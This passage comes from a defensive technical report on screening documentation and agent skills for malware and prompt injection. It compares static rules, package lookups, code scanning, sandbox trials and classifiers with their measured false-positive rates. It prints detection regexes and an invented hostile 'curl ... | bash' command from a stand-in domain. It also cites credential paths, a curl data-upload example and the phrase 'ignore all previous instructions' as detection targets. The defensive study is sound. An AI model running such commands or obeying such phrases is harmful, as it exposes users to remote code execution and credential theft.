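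Context7's *on premise* describes a version that stores private documentation in the customer's infrastructure, although the customer's chosen AI providers still receive the content needed for processing. Its content policies let administrators restrict which public documentation their agents can use, but don't affect private content indexed locally.

Private sources still carry some risk. *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (2026) considers an attacker who may contribute text through a legitimate account on a platform that requires a login. Someone who stole an employee's password could edit an internal setup guide, and an honest employee could paste in a poisoned README from a public project. The damage could be greater, because an agent that reads internal documentation may have access to internal systems. Anthropic advises companies to review skills from internal contributors as carefully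 as those from third parties.

Under a copy of Upstash's terms from September 2025, customers are responsible for keeping malware out of what they submit and for checking the output before using it in production. A service could help by screening private content within the customer's systems and sending warnings to the customer's own administrators. That would keep the text away from outside reviewers and avoid silently removing passages.

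### Other documentation services and skill hubs

Comparable accounts from other documentation services are hard to find. SotaDocs, which also supplies documentation to agents, describes encryption, access controls and temporary isolated workers for indexing private content. These measures protect the documentation from outsiders but don't stop an agent from reading harmful content in it.

Skill hubs have published more, and Yang and colleagues list the scanners that five of them use:

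| Hub | Scanners |
|---|---|
| ClawHub | Its own static rules, NVIDIA's SkillSpector, Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard |
| skillmd.com | Its own static rules, Cisco's skill-scanner, SkillSpector |
| skills.sh | Gen Agent Trust Hub, Snyk Agent Scan, Socket |
| SkillsMP | None |
| skills.rest | None |

SkillsMP indexes over four million skill files, so anyone who installs from it has to rely on checks elsewhere. Developers can run some of the same scanners themselves with OpenClaw's *ClawScan* (2026), a free tool that applies SkillSpector and skill-scanner to a local folder.

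A hub can run a scanner without always following its advice. Following SkillSpector's recommendations would have meant blocking 45.8% of the ClawHub skills for which the researchers had results. ClawHub combines several sources of evidence. The Hacker News' *OpenClaw Integrates VirusTotal Scanning to Detect Malicious ClawHub Skills* (2026) describes an early version of its screening, which used Google's malware-scanning service VirusTotal. The hub approved skills that VirusTotal classified as benign, put a warning on suspicious ones and blocked malicious ones. It also rescanned active skills every day in case a harmless one had changed.

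According to OpenClaw, the hub's own risk analysis now weighs a skill's files and declared permissions along with results from VirusTotal and other scanners. The hub's static rules contribute evidence, but neither they nor AI-Infra-Guard can block an installation alone. The main test is whether the skill's content and the access it requests match what a user would expect from its description. An owner who thinks the hub wrongly flagged a skill can request a rescan with a single command and, in some cases, appeal to OpenClaw.

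## Rules that match text patterns

A static rule is a fixed test that a detector applies to a text without running any code in it or using a language model to interpret it. Most static rules are text patterns. They need little compute, work offline and give the same result every time, so many detectors use them, alone or as a first stage. Some have had very high false-positive rates.

### From a pattern to a verdict

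Aguara's *Custom rules*, part of the manual for a scanner of that name, has a harmless sample rule that finds references to a company's internal web addresses. Its main pattern is a regular expression, a formula that describes a set of strings:

`https?://internal\.mycompany\.com`

The question mark makes the "s" before it optional, so the pattern matches both `http` and `https`. Each backslash makes the dot after it match only a literal dot, since a dot alone would match any character. The rule also lists the plain string `api.internal`, and either pattern is enough for a match. The rule applies only to Markdown and text files, and it excludes text that contains the heading `## documentation`. Exclusions like this reduce false alarms, but an attacker who knows about one can add the same heading to avoid a match.

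Whoever writes a rule sets its severity before seeing the text it will scan, based on what such a match usually means. The sample rule's severity is HIGH. Cisco's *Skill scanner* rates a production API key written into the code as critical, an instruction to adopt a new persona as high, and a tool with a non-standard address as medium. Some scanners adjust the severity depending on where the match appears. *ctxsentry*, an open-source tool that checks a repository before a coding agent opens it, rates the same string as medium in a source code comment and critical in `CLAUDE.md`, because agents load that file as authoritative instructions.

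A detector records each match as a finding, then turns its findings into a verdict. Yang, Ying and colleagues describe several ways to do this. Cisco's skill-scanner blocks a skill over a single finding rated HIGH or CRITICAL. NVIDIA's SkillSpector adds up the severity scores, multiplies the sum by a coefficient if the skill contains executable scripts, and blocks the skill if the result reaches a fixed threshold. A community detector called skillscan-security also gives each finding a confidence score. Under the strict policy the researchers used, it ignores findings with confidence below 0.75, then blocks the skill if any remaining finding matches a designated blocking rule or the combined score reaches 70.

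Adding up scores lets several weak signs count together, but it also tends to give longer texts higher scores. A threshold tuned for whole skills would therefore probably be too high for a single chunk of documentation.

### Where the patterns come from

SkillGate, a detector by Yang, Fu and colleagues, starts with 530 patterns, 428 of them derived from MITRE ATT&CK. The US non-profit MITRE maintains this public catalogue of attackers' techniques, which is grouped by the attacker's goal. For example, searching files for passwords comes under "credential access". According to MITRE's *Updates* (2025), the October 2025 version covers 910 pieces of software, 176 groups and 55 campaigns.

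Defence evasion, or hiding from security tools, is the largest category in SkillGate's ATT&CK patterns, with 62. Execution and risky commands have 56 each, credential access has 44 and persistence has 38. Sending data out, the final step of most credential thefts, has only 27.

The other 102 patterns come from Sigma, an open format for rules that search logs of computer events, such as a program starting. SigmaHQ, which publishes more than 3,000 of these rules, compares Sigma's role for logs to YARA's role for files. YARA is a pattern language that malware analysts use to recognize files, and Cisco's *Architecture* lists it among skill-scanner's methods.

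ATT&CK and Sigma describe events on a machine, so applying them to documentation causes problems. Unlike a log entry, a command in a manual is not evidence that anything ran, and the writer may have included it as a warning.

Even a command that did run may be weak evidence of malware. Palo Alto Networks' *Run downloaded script using pipe* describes an alert for machines that download a script and run it immediately. The alert's severity is "Informational", and analysts are expected to check whether the process is benign and whether someone wanted it to run. A screener that has only a chunk of text can't make these checks, because it can't examine the machine as an analyst can.

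### What the patterns look for

The best-known rules match commands that download a script and run it. For example, in `curl -LsSf https://astral.sh/uv/install.sh | sh`, `curl` downloads a script and the pipe (`|`) passes it to `sh`, which runs it. This command is harmless and installs uv, a Python package manager. Yet it contains a standard malware-related pattern, and it appears in the *Quick Start* for Cisco's own security scanner, skill-scanner.

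Rules for credential paths match locations where software stores secrets. SkillGate gives its highest severity to `.aws/credentials`, where Amazon's command-line tools store access keys. A beginner's guide to those tools might include the sentence "Save your access key in `~/.aws/credentials`." The pattern matches that sentence as well as an instruction to copy a key from the file.

Another group of rules detects outbound data transfer. One SkillGate pattern matches a `curl` command that uploads a file, such as `curl --data @/tmp/order.json https://api.shop.example/orders`, which could appear in any manual for an online ordering system. *ctxsentry* also flags suspicious destinations such as ngrok and webhook.site, which can give anyone an address for receiving data and are useful both to data thieves and to developers testing an application. It also flags commands that hide a file's contents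 in the domain name of a DNS query.

Persistence means arranging for a program to start again after the user closes it or restarts the computer. SkillGate looks for commands that add a line to `.bashrc`, a file of commands that the shell runs whenever the user opens a new terminal. Malware can restart itself this way. But installation guides often tell readers to add a line to the same file so that the shell can find a newly installed tool:

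`echo 'export PATH="$HOME/bin:$PATH"' >> ~/.bashrc`

Encoded payloads hide commands or instructions from text patterns by changing how they are written. Base64, the most common encoding, represents any data as letters, digits and a few symbols. SkillGate has a critical-severity pattern for text that decodes Base64 and passes the result directly to the shell, which legitimate documentation rarely does. Base64 alone is much more common in legitimate documentation. For example, a page about storing secrets in Kubernetes could easily include `cGFzc3dvcmQ=`, which is "password" in Base64. A scanner can avoid many false alarms by decoding such strings first and applying its rules to the result, as *ctxsentry* does for Base64 and hexadecimal.

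Some attackers hide text from human readers but leave it in the data the model receives. Zero-width characters take up no space on the screen, so an attacker can insert them into a forbidden phrase to keep a rule from matching it. An attacker can also spell out an entire instruction in Unicode "tag" characters, which most programs don't display. ctxsentry decodes the tag characters, strips the zero-width ones, replaces Greek and Cyrillic look-alikes with Latin letters, and runs all its rules again. But zero-width characters also have legitimate uses. Persian spelling requires one inside many words, and another joins smaller emoji into a single one. SkillGate's rule requires a cluster of zero-width characters, so it shouldn't flag most Persian text.

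Terminal control codes can hide text in a similar way. They begin with a special "escape" byte and make a terminal change colours or move the cursor, which can conceal or overwrite text on the screen. They also appear in harmless text, such as a test log, pasted from a terminal, that shows passed tests in green. The MCP wrapper from Trail of Bits can replace the escape byte with the visible letters "ESC", which disables the codes and lets a reviewer see where they were. This method doesn't require judging whether the text is malicious, and harmless text loses only some colour.

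The last family consists of phrases that sound like instructions to a model, such as "ignore all previous instructions". According to Yang, Ying and colleagues, skillscan-security matches known phrases and also scores combinations of words such as "ignore" and "instructions". "Ignore the installation instructions above if you use Docker" contains both words but is harmless. One rule in ctxsentry matches only sentences that address an AI, assistant or agent and also name an action such as running or installing something. That should reduce false positives in most manuals, though less in manuals for agent software. According to the tool's documentation, harmless pages about prompt injection will still produce findings, and an attacker can get past the patterns with a new paraphrase.

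### Combinations and data flow

Mentioning a password or contacting a server is usually harmless on its own, so a combination rule requires two signals. For example, skillscan-security has rules that flag a skill if it both reads a secret and communicates over the network. These rules avoid flagging a page that merely explains where the credentials are.

Unfortunately, the two signals can also occur together by chance. This invented Python code reads a key, checks that it isn't empty, and then asks an unrelated server for the time:

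```python
key = os.environ["WEATHER_KEY"]
print("Key found:", bool(key))
requests.get("https://time.example/now")
```

The next example sends the key to a server:

```python
key = os.environ["WEATHER_KEY"]
requests.get("https://api.weather.example/today",
             headers={"X-Key": key})
```

A combination rule flags both examples. Data-flow analysis can distinguish them because it traces whether the secret reaches the network. The analyser parses the code into parts such as assignments and function calls. It marks the value from a sensitive source, here the environment variable, and follows it through every variable and function that receives it. It reports a problem only if the marked value reaches a sensitive operation such as a network request. In the time example, the key never leaves the machine, so the analyser reports nothing.

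By default, Cisco's skill-scanner does this for shell commands that pass their output to one another through pipes. For program code, users can switch on a similar analysis that also connects findings across files. Cisco's separate scanner for MCP servers is more thorough. It treats everything a tool receives as untrusted and traces it through the whole program, including the utility code where malicious behaviour is often hidden.

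The weather example still triggers an alarm, although a client of a paid weather service normally has to send its key to prove that it has an account. If `api.weather.example` belonged to a thief instead of the company that issued the key, the same code would steal the key. Data-flow analysis can show that a secret leaves the machine, and often where it goes, but not whether the recipient should have it.

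This kind of analysis also works poorly on documentation. Examples often leave out the surrounding program or replace part of it with three dots, so the analyser may be unable to parse them. A plain-language request to send someone the contents of a secrets file has no variables to follow. Chunking causes a further problem for both methods, because if the code that reads a secret and the code that sends it fall in different chunks, neither chunk contains both signals. A documentation service could avoid this by running such rules on the whole page before splitting it.

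### Two commands that match the same rule

A simple rule for download-and-run commands could use this pattern:

`curl\s.*\|\s*(ba)?sh\b`

The rule matches the word `curl`, a space, any other characters, a pipe, and then either `sh` or `bash`. The `\b` at the end requires the word to stop there. Without it, the rule would also flag commands that pass a download to `shasum`, which only computes a checksum. A careful user might do this before running anything.

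The first command below is the official way to install SDKMAN, the tool whose installation command another scanner flagged in the study by Yang, Ying and colleagues. The second is an invented hostile version:

```bash
curl -s "https://get.sdkman.io" | bash
curl -s "https://get-sdkman.example" | bash
```

Only the addresses differ, and they fall under the `.*` in the pattern, which accepts anything. The rule therefore produces the same finding with the same severity for both commands. The differences that matter are in facts that the rule doesn't use:

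| Fact | Official command | Hostile command |
|---|---|---|
| Matches the rule | Yes | Yes |
| Owner of the web address | The SDKMAN project | An attacker |
| Appears on SDKMAN's own website | Yes | No |
| What the downloaded script does | Installs SDKMAN | Installs malware |

The owner of the address is the easiest of these facts to add. A sample policy for Cisco's skill-scanner lists known installer domains, including `sh.rustup.rs`, which serves the installer for the Rust programming language. A service could add `get.sdkman.io` to such a list, but the list would need constant maintenance, and a new project would trigger alarms until someone added its domain.

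A list of domains also fails when many people share a domain. Cisco's *Curl installer* gives a command of the same form for DefenseClaw, Cisco's tool for controlling what agents may install. The command downloads a script from `raw.githubusercontent.com`, which serves files from any public GitHub repository, including an attacker's, so the list would have to name the exact repository. The remaining fact to check is what the script contains, and Cisco's page recommends running the command only "after review". A screener has to download the script to check it, and the script's owner can change it later, like the DNS record in the 0DIN case.

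The same sample policy has the settings `demote_in_docs` and `demote_instructional`, which apparently lower the severity of such commands in documentation and instructional text. This makes sense for a skill, where a command in a reference file is less likely to run than one in a script. In a documentation service, nearly everything is documentation, so the settings would lower the severity of the hostile command too.

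### Results on SkillsBench

Yang, Fu and colleagues measured how well static rules work on SkillsBench, a set of 1,500 benign skills from public repositories and 150 handwritten malicious ones. They tested skill-scanner's static mode at each of its five severity thresholds. At the MEDIUM threshold, for example, it flags any skill with at least one finding rated MEDIUM or higher. The researchers also tested ClawVet, a scanner with 54 patterns, and SkillGate's 530 patterns without the language model that normally makes the final decision.

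| Detector and threshold | Malicious skills flagged (of 150) | Recall | Benign skills flagged (of 1,500) | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner, INFO | 123 | 82.0% | 1,297 | 86.5% |
| skill-scanner, LOW | 72 | 48.0% | 280 | 18.7% |
| skill-scanner, MEDIUM | 71 | 47.3% | 261 | 17.4% |
| skill-scanner, HIGH | 10 | 6.7% | 19 | 1.3% |
| skill-scanner, CRITICAL | 7 | 4.7% | 9 | 0.6% |
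| ClawVet | 134 | 89.3% | 756 | 50.4% |
| SkillGate's patterns alone | 135 | 90.0% | 406 | 27.1% |

At the INFO threshold, skill-scanner flagged a larger share of the benign skills than of the malicious ones, so a flag was very weak evidence that a skill was benign. At CRITICAL, it rarely flagged benign skills but missed 143 of the 150 malicious ones. The settings in between also performed poorly. MEDIUM, for example, missed more than half of the malicious skills and still flagged about one benign skill in six.

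SkillGate has almost ten times as many patterns as ClawVet. Its patterns caught nearly the same number of malicious skills but flagged only about half as many benign ones. The number of patterns evidently matters less than how precisely they describe an attack. SkillGate's own developers made the comparison, although they gave ClawVet an advantage by choosing the threshold that worked best for it on the test set. The malicious skills were handmade, so the recall figures may not hold for real attacks. The false-positive rates are more realistic because the benign skills are real, but these rates are for whole skills, not chunks of documentation.

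Better exclusions can also remove many false alarms. *ctxsentry*'s developer ran it on a working repository of 3,300 files and adjusted it until the number of findings fell from 733 to 5. The tool still caught every attack in its own benchmark, but that benchmark has only 20 attacks and 25 harmless texts, and the project's automated tests fail if the score gets worse. The perfect score is therefore weak evidence that the tool would catch attacks its developer didn't think of. The tool also lets people silence a finding with a comment next to the flagged line. A documentation service would have to disable that feature, because an attacker could add the comment too.

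Changing the severity threshold is a cruder fix than rewriting the rules. Raising skill-scanner's threshold from MEDIUM to HIGH removes 242 false alarms, but also 61 of the 71 correct detections. All 303 of these skills had MEDIUM as their highest severity, so any threshold flags either all of them or none.

Raising a rule's severity has the same problem. Yang, Ying and colleagues found that skillscan-security detected undeclared network access in a skill that uploads customer data, but let the skill through because the rule that fired, PSV-001, has only MEDIUM severity. A higher severity would have blocked the skill, but PSV-001 fires on 48.3% of malicious skills and 29.3% of benign ones, so the change would also block many legitimate skills. If 1% of skills were malicious, a PSV-001 finding would raise the probability that a skill is malicious to only about 1.6%.

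To do better, a detector needs information that distinguishes the skills within a severity level, such as who receives the customer data and whether the user agreed to send it. Neither the severity score nor the match that produced it contains that information. The two SDKMAN commands have identical scores, so any threshold that lets the official command through also lets the hostile one through.

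## Checks on packages, publishers and behaviour

To find facts that a text rule can't, a screener can check whether a package exists in a registry, read the package's code, consider who published the documentation, or have an agent follow the instructions in isolation and record what happens. Most of these checks take longer than pattern matching, and each produces its own false positives.

### Looking up names and addresses

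The screener first extracts the package names, versions and web addresses from the commands in a chunk. The command usually shows which registry to query. `pip install` uses PyPI unless the command or the machine's settings name another server, while `npx`, `bunx`, `pnpm dlx` and `yarn dlx` all use npm, according to Eriksen's *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*. The screener then checks whether the package exists, when it was first published, which account controls it, and whether it is on a list of known malware. For a web address, the registration record gives the domain's age, although privacy services often hide the owner. An address at a shared hosting company needs a separate test, because the company's own domain stays registered after a customer abandons a site.

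Eriksen is the Aikido researcher who registered an npm name that a language model had invented. The name was `react-codeshift`, apparently a blend of two real tools, `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod`. He traced it to a commit of 17 October 2025 that added 47 model-written skills to a repository. They included this command:

`npx react-codeshift --transform=react-codeshift/transforms/new-jsx-transform.js ./src`

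The command has no piped script, credential path or hidden characters, so most text rules would not flag it. Eriksen registered the name on 14 January 2026. The table shows what a lookup would have returned before and after that date.

| Question | December 2025 | 15 January 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Does the package exist on npm? | No | Yes |
| How old is it? | – | One day |
| Is it older than the text that recommends it? | – | No, about three months younger |

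In December, the package doesn't exist, which is enough to justify a flag. In January, it does exist, so a screener that checks only for existence would let the command through, even though the command could now run a stranger's code. The screener could still catch the problem by checking whether the package is newer than the documentation, because genuine documentation seldom recommends a package before it exists. Vendors sometimes publish documentation before a release, so this rule would need an exception for packages from the vendor's own account.

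Download counts would have been less useful. Eriksen's empty package had about 74 downloads on its first day, which he attributes to registry mirrors and security scanners. After that it had one to four a day, which he attributes to agents following the skills.

Bagmar and Saraf found that Claude Code, Copilot CLI, Codex CLI and Cursor's agent don't automatically check package names, sources or versions, and instead rely on the model or the user to notice a problem. Adding a security warning to the prompt helped only with the kind of problem it mentioned. They therefore built a check that uses fixed rules to verify the name, source and version just before installation, and they report that it closes most of the gap.

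### Why one lookup is not enough

A package name can be harmless when a service indexes a page that mentions it, but dangerous a month later if its owner has abandoned it and someone else has claimed it. A reader's comment on Schneier's *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (2026) quotes Alon Hertz, one of the researchers behind the `llms.txt` study, making this point.

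The service could save the package names it extracts from each chunk and look them up again every day. This should require fairly few lookups, since thousands of chunks about one framework are likely to mention the same few packages. Rescanning the text would not catch a stale name, because the text hasn't changed. The monitoring that Context7 describes would not help either, because it covers content its classifier has already flagged, and a stale name would probably be in a chunk that passed.

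A daily lookup can still miss a poisoned release of an established package, because the package's name and age look normal and the lookup can't flag the release until someone adds it to a malware list. Nesbitt (2026), in *Package Security Problems for AI Agents*, reports that coding agents automatically installed a poisoned npm release, which he calls nx/debug, with a backdoor that stole SSH keys (used to log in to other machines) and API tokens.

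Equinor, the Norwegian energy company, advises its developers to consider waiting until a release is a week old before installing it, unless it fixes an important security problem, because people usually identify malicious updates within a few days. A documentation service can't easily apply this advice because most installation commands don't specify a version, and the installer picks the newest release when the command runs. The delay has to be set on the developer's machine or on a company's package server.

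### False alarms from lookups

Internal packages are the most obvious source of false alarms. A company's private setup guide may name dozens of packages that exist only on its own server, and a PyPI lookup would find none of them. The screener can avoid this by also querying the company's server, but a public documentation service normally can't access that server.

These alarms still have some use, because an attacker can exploit an internal name that nobody has registered publicly. In an attack called dependency confusion, the attacker publishes a package under that name, and the installer picks it over the private one. Bagmar and Saraf cite the `torchtriton` case, in which an attacker published a package on PyPI under the name of one of PyTorch's internal dependencies. The package stole SSH keys and environment variables from people who ran the standard installation. A warning about an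 internal name could prompt the company to reserve it, but removing the page would only remove correct instructions.

Checking where packages come from has a similar problem. PyTorch distributes builds for Nvidia graphics cards from its own package server, whose address appears in over 10,000 `requirements.txt` files on GitHub (again a rough count). A rule that allows only PyPI would flag all of these files.

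Domain checks often treat an unfamiliar address as suspicious. Gen Agent Trust Hub's *context7* (2026), an automated audit on the hub skills.sh, notes that Context7's own website, context7.com, is missing from the scanner's list of trusted domains, but accepts that the connection fits the skill's purpose. The scanner's audit of another *context7* skill, 12 days later, lists the same connection under data exfiltration because the domain is not a recognized service. It still rates the skill safe overall, so the finding did little harm, but a hub that blocked skills on any such finding would have blocked a legitimate one.

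General website checkers are no more consistent. Gridinsoft's *Context7.com Reviews* labels the site both "Young Domain" and "High Trust Score". ScanMalware's *Security Scan Report* counts a domain age of over 180 days in the site's favour but also reports that the domain's age is unavailable. It marks the site down for a low ranking and for links to GitHub repositories that it flags as malicious, though a service as large as Context7 is bound to link to some strange repositories.

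Checks for misspelled names look for packages whose names resemble those of popular ones. They can catch `tdqm`, a live PyPI package that imitates the progress-bar library `tqdm` and appears in over 960 `requirements.txt` files. But a similar rule could flag `preact`, a well-known JavaScript library whose name is one letter longer than `react`.

Version checks also produce false positives. Yang and colleagues examined 2,790 findings behind false positives from skill detectors and attributed 77 of them, about 3%, to concerns about dependencies. SkillSpector's rule SC4, which searches a vulnerability database, accounted for 57% of those 77. It often dropped or simplified the skill's version requirements before searching. Suppose a skill requires `imagetool>=2.5`, an invented package, and the database lists a vulnerability fixed in version 2.3. The installer can't choose an affected version,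 but if the rule searches for `imagetool` alone, it still reports the old vulnerability.

This error is relatively easy to fix, because getting it right only requires comparing version numbers. The other 43% of the dependency findings concerned suspicious names or packages with no pinned version. Documentation would trigger many of the findings about unpinned versions, since the usual `pip install` line omits the version so that readers get the current one.

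### Scanning the package's code

A registry can confirm that a package exists, but not that it is safe. A screener can download the package and analyse its code without installing it. *MALGUARD* (Gao, Sun and colleagues, 2025) describes a detector that does this for Python packages without sending every package to a language model.

MalGuard is based on the observation that malicious and benign packages use sensitive functions differently. It parses each package into a graph showing which functions call which, then measures how central each function is. The simplest measure, degree centrality, divides the number of connections a function has by the number of other functions in the graph. In a graph of 11 functions, one with four connections scores 4/10, or 0.4.

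The best version of MalGuard uses Katz centrality, which also gives a function credit for being close to other central functions:

C(v) = α × (sum of C(u) over every function u connected to v) + β

Here α is a small number that reduces the influence of distant connections, and β is a baseline every function gets. Malicious Python packages are often short scripts whose functions don't call each other, so a dangerous function can score zero. The researchers therefore add 1 to every score.

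To choose which functions to watch, they averaged each function's score across known malicious packages and took the top 500. GPT-3.5-turbo, an old language model, then removed functions with no plausible malicious use, such as `print`. In the Katz version, 294 remained. A random forest, which combines the votes of many decision trees, then classifies a package from its scores for these functions. Another algorithm, LIME, finds the ten functions that most influenced the classification, so that a reviewer can look them up in the code.

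This approach can avoid some false alarms that a list of sensitive functions produces. GuardDog, Datadog's rule-based scanner, wrongly flagged the package GACF because it copied environment variables, started other programs and created folders. MalGuard passed it because most of those functions played only a minor part in the package.

The researchers tested MalGuard on a fifth of a collection of 9,664 malicious packages and 10,000 popular benign ones. It reached 99.6% precision and 98.4% recall, compared with 95.6% and 82.6% for GuardDog. These figures imply that MalGuard flagged about 8 of some 2,000 benign packages, a false-positive rate of roughly 0.4%.

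The researchers then ran MalGuard on all 64,348 packages uploaded to PyPI over about five weeks from 21 December 2024. It flagged 144, and manual review confirmed 113 as malicious. PyPI removed 109 of those. The false-positive rate was about 0.05%, but precision fell to 78% because malicious packages were much rarer than in the test set. Recall on these packages is unknown because the researchers reviewed only the flagged ones.

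Of the 31 false alarms, 25 were demonstration packages that users uploaded as tests, and six were pranks, such as one that displays "Crazy Thursday" messages. Few manuals would recommend any of these, so screening documentation might produce fewer false alarms than screening new uploads. But MalGuard's benign training examples were packages with more than 1,000 downloads and at least 90 days on PyPI, so it may be less reliable for the small projects that a documentation service also indexes.

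Attackers also change their methods, so users have to keep retraining such scanners. In a related experiment, the researchers trained simpler models, including a random forest, on packages from 2021 and 2022. The random forest's recall fell from 82% on packages from that period to 59% on those from 2023 and 52% on those from 2024, and its precision fell from 97% to 73%. The researchers say MalGuard is fast enough for daily updates.

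A package scan also has to examine the copy that the agent will install, which may come from a second server that the README adds. Only a version check will catch old releases that have known vulnerabilities but no malicious code.

### Publisher reputation

Reputation scores are based on who published the documentation. Context7 introduced its score to deal with copies of popular libraries. In an example from Upstash, a search for Next.js returns Vercel's official documentation, with 9,372 snippets, and a copy in another account, with 9,375. Both have a quality score of 82.2, and the copy's description calls it "the most comprehensive and trustable" documentation, so an agent has little reason to choose the original. Upstash's reputation label depends on the organization instead of the repository and drops for cloned repositories. The original gets "High" and the copy "Low", so the agent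 chooses the original.

Shannon lists the signals behind what Context7 later called its trust score:

| Type of source | Signals |
|---|---|
| Repository | Number of repositories the account owns, total stars, account age, activity, followers, completeness of the profile |
| Website | Encrypted connection (TLS), overall presentation, domain authority, number of links from elsewhere, number of different domains that link to it |

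Some of these signals are easy to produce, since anyone can fill in a profile or get a free certificate for encrypted connections. Account age is harder to fake, although an attacker could take over an old account. Attackers can also manufacture popularity, as Noma pointed out about ContextCrush. Equinor warns of starjacking, in which a publisher links a package to an unrelated popular repository. This works because the registry doesn't check the link. Context7 counts stars across the account's own repositories, so starjacking shouldn't raise a Context7 score, but it could mislead a screener that judges packages by the repositories they link to.

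Context7 also gives a verified checkmark to libraries that have a trust score of at least 9, are among the 100 most used with a trust score of at least 6, or have been claimed by their owner. A claim seems to establish only who controls the library, so an attacker could presumably publish a repository and claim it. In February 2026 the checkmark had no effect on ranking, but Upstash planned to include it. If it does, claimed libraries will need to meet a further condition, or an attacker could improve a library's ranking just by claiming it.

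A good reputation is also weak evidence against the kind of error in the `llms.txt` study, where the documentation came from large, established companies. It doesn't rule out a compromise either. Bagmar and Saraf mention the attack on Ultralytics, a project with 8.9 million downloads a month from PyPI. A pull request (a proposed change) labelled as a README edit led to releases containing cryptocurrency miners.

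Reputation scores hurt new and small projects most. An honest developer's first library comes from a new account with few stars or followers. If Context7 ranks it below an established alternative, agents use it less, which also keeps it out of the top 100, so claiming the library is the only realistic way to get the checkmark. The penalty for cloned repositories could also hurt a legitimate fork, such as one whose maintainers took over after the original developers stopped work.

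The score does limited harm if it affects only ranking. A developer who asks for an unusual library by name should still find its documentation, because few other results compete with it. Using the same score to block content would be much harsher, because every new project would look suspicious until it had attracted users, and it might need the documentation service to attract them.

### Trial runs

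In a trial run, an agent follows the instructions in a sandbox (an isolated environment) while other software records its actions. Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026) tested this on skills in *The Devil Wears Markdown*. They put each skill in an isolated container with its own files and gave Claude Opus 4.8 up to five minutes to try it with harmless dummy data. They recorded calls to the operating system, network traffic and file changes.

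The agent was told to skip anything dangerous, such as reading real credentials or running unknown code from the internet, and to record what it skipped and why. If the agent reports, for example, that it refused to send out a password, the analysis counts this as strong evidence only if the skill actually contains the instruction to send it.

The software gives each suspicious pattern a base score of 40, 70 or 100 according to severity and multiplies it by a factor for the quality of the evidence. The factor is 0.45 for a remark by the agent that nothing in the skill supports, 0.70 for an instruction in the skill that the agent didn't carry out, 1.00 for an action that the records show, and 1.15 if several records agree. Weak evidence can score at most 25 or 30, while a clearly dangerous instruction that the agent blocked scores at least 85. The total is:

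score = min(100, highest pattern score + 0.1 × sum of the others + bonus)

Independent pieces of evidence add a bonus of up to 15 points, and a total of 35 or more counts as malicious. One medium-severity instruction found in the skill but not carried out scores 70 × 0.70 = 49, above the threshold. Two weak findings at the 25-point limit score 25 + 2.5 = 27.5 without a bonus, below the threshold. The researchers describe the score as a rule of thumb rather than a probability, and did not test how much the results depend on the chosen numbers.

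A group of language models makes the final decision. They receive the skill, the record of the trial and the matches from 58,674 static rules. The researchers collected 400 malicious and 300 benign skills, used 560 to develop the system, and tested it on the remaining 140. They repeated the test with some of the evidence withheld:

| Evidence given to the models | Malicious skills flagged (of 80) | Recall | Benign skills flagged (of 60) | False-positive rate |
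|---|---|---|---|---|
| Skill only | 54 | 68% | 21 | 35% |
| Skill and static rules | 28 | 35% | 3 | 5% |
| Skill and trial run | 63 | 79% | 5 | 8% |
| Skill, static rules and trial run | 68 | 85% | 5 | 8% |

The trial run reduced false alarms and caught more attacks, whereas the static rules alone reduced false alarms but missed most attacks. Cisco's skill-scanner, with a small language model, also caught 68 of the 80 malicious skills, but it flagged 40 of the benign ones. That comparison is less informative because the new system used a much larger model. The test also had only 60 benign skills, so the true false-positive rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 4% to 18%. Of the 300 benign skills, 200 came from a curated list without a separate security review, so a few may have deserved a flag.

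All five false alarms in the full system also appeared when the models had only the skill and the trial run. One of them was `research-lookup`, a skill for finding information online. Its setup instructions download an installer from the supplier and run it, and its script sends an API key to the service that needs it. The skill scored 27.5 in the trial run, below the threshold. The final report gives 100% confidence that the trial found no evidence of malware and that the installation command is harmless. It also gives 92% confidence that the same command is remote code execution and 90% that the use of the key is data theft. The verdict was malware, with a score of 92.

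So the trial score was right, but the later stage overruled it. Treating a low score as final would have prevented this error, but it would also let through attacks that do nothing malicious during the trial. Malware may activate only on a certain date, after a particular input or when a real credential is present, and Gao and colleagues note that attackers often read environment variables to avoid this kind of analysis. Truong-Le and colleagues ran each skill only once and did not test attackers who knew about the system.

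The safety rules also limit what the agent can detect. Because it must not run unknown code from the internet, it would skip both SDKMAN's official installation command and the malicious imitation, leaving much the same record for each. Seeing the difference would require running the installers. Equinor suggests testing packages in a container, a virtual machine or an online workspace without any secrets, which limits the damage, but malware may still not show harmful behaviour during the test.

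All these results are for skills, and documentation would be harder to test. A chunk may contain half a program, or need a database that the sandbox doesn't have. Commands would therefore often fail, and the researchers rightly don't count failures as signs of malice. At five minutes each, running the 9,372 Next.js snippets one after another would also take more than a month.

Testing each library once would be more practical. Pandex did something similar when it had agents build small projects from vendors' documentation. Context7 already has an agent that researches its weak answers, and it could in principle record that agent's network connections and installations. A trial like this would cover only the pages the agent used, but it could reveal a package that no longer exists or an installer that contacts an unexpected server.

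## Classifiers and language models that judge content in context

A static rule matches a credential path wherever it appears, but a trained classifier or an LLM judge can take the rest of the text into account. A trained classifier learns from labelled examples to sort text into categories, here harmful and harmless. An LLM judge is a large language model prompted to decide whether the content is malicious. Classifiers are usually smaller and cheaper to run, but a judge can compare a command with the stated purpose of a skill or page and give reasons for its verdict.

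### Comparing a sentence with the text around it

A classifier needs numbers as input, so a neural network called an encoder first converts each passage of text into a fixed-length list of numbers, known as an embedding. Passages with similar meanings get similar embeddings even if they share few words, which is also how Context7 can search by meaning.

Liu, Ma and Vorobeychik (2026), in *Robust Context-Aware Detection of Malicious Instructions in Text*, use embeddings to find prompt injections in text that an agent fetches. Their method, context-aware detection (CAD), splits the text into sentences and describes each sentence in two ways:

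- The sentence alone: φ(sentence)
- Its effect on the whole: φ([q; s]) − φ([q; s] without the sentence)

Here φ is the encoder, q is the user's query, s is the document, and [q; s] is the query followed by the document. Suppose an embedding had only two numbers, and the query and document together had the embedding (0.62, 0.30), which became (0.61, 0.10) when one sentence was removed from the document. The difference is (0.01, 0.20), so the sentence barely affects the first number but changes the second a lot. A sentence that an attacker has inserted should change the embedding differently from one that belongs in the document.

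CAD's real embeddings have 1,024 numbers each, so the two descriptions together give 2,048 numbers per sentence. A small neural network turns these into a probability that the sentence is malicious. CAD deletes every sentence with a probability above 0.5 and passes the rest to the agent. The researchers trained only this network and left the encoder unchanged. For training data, they had a language model write documents, queries and malicious goals, then inserted malicious instructions at random points in the documents.

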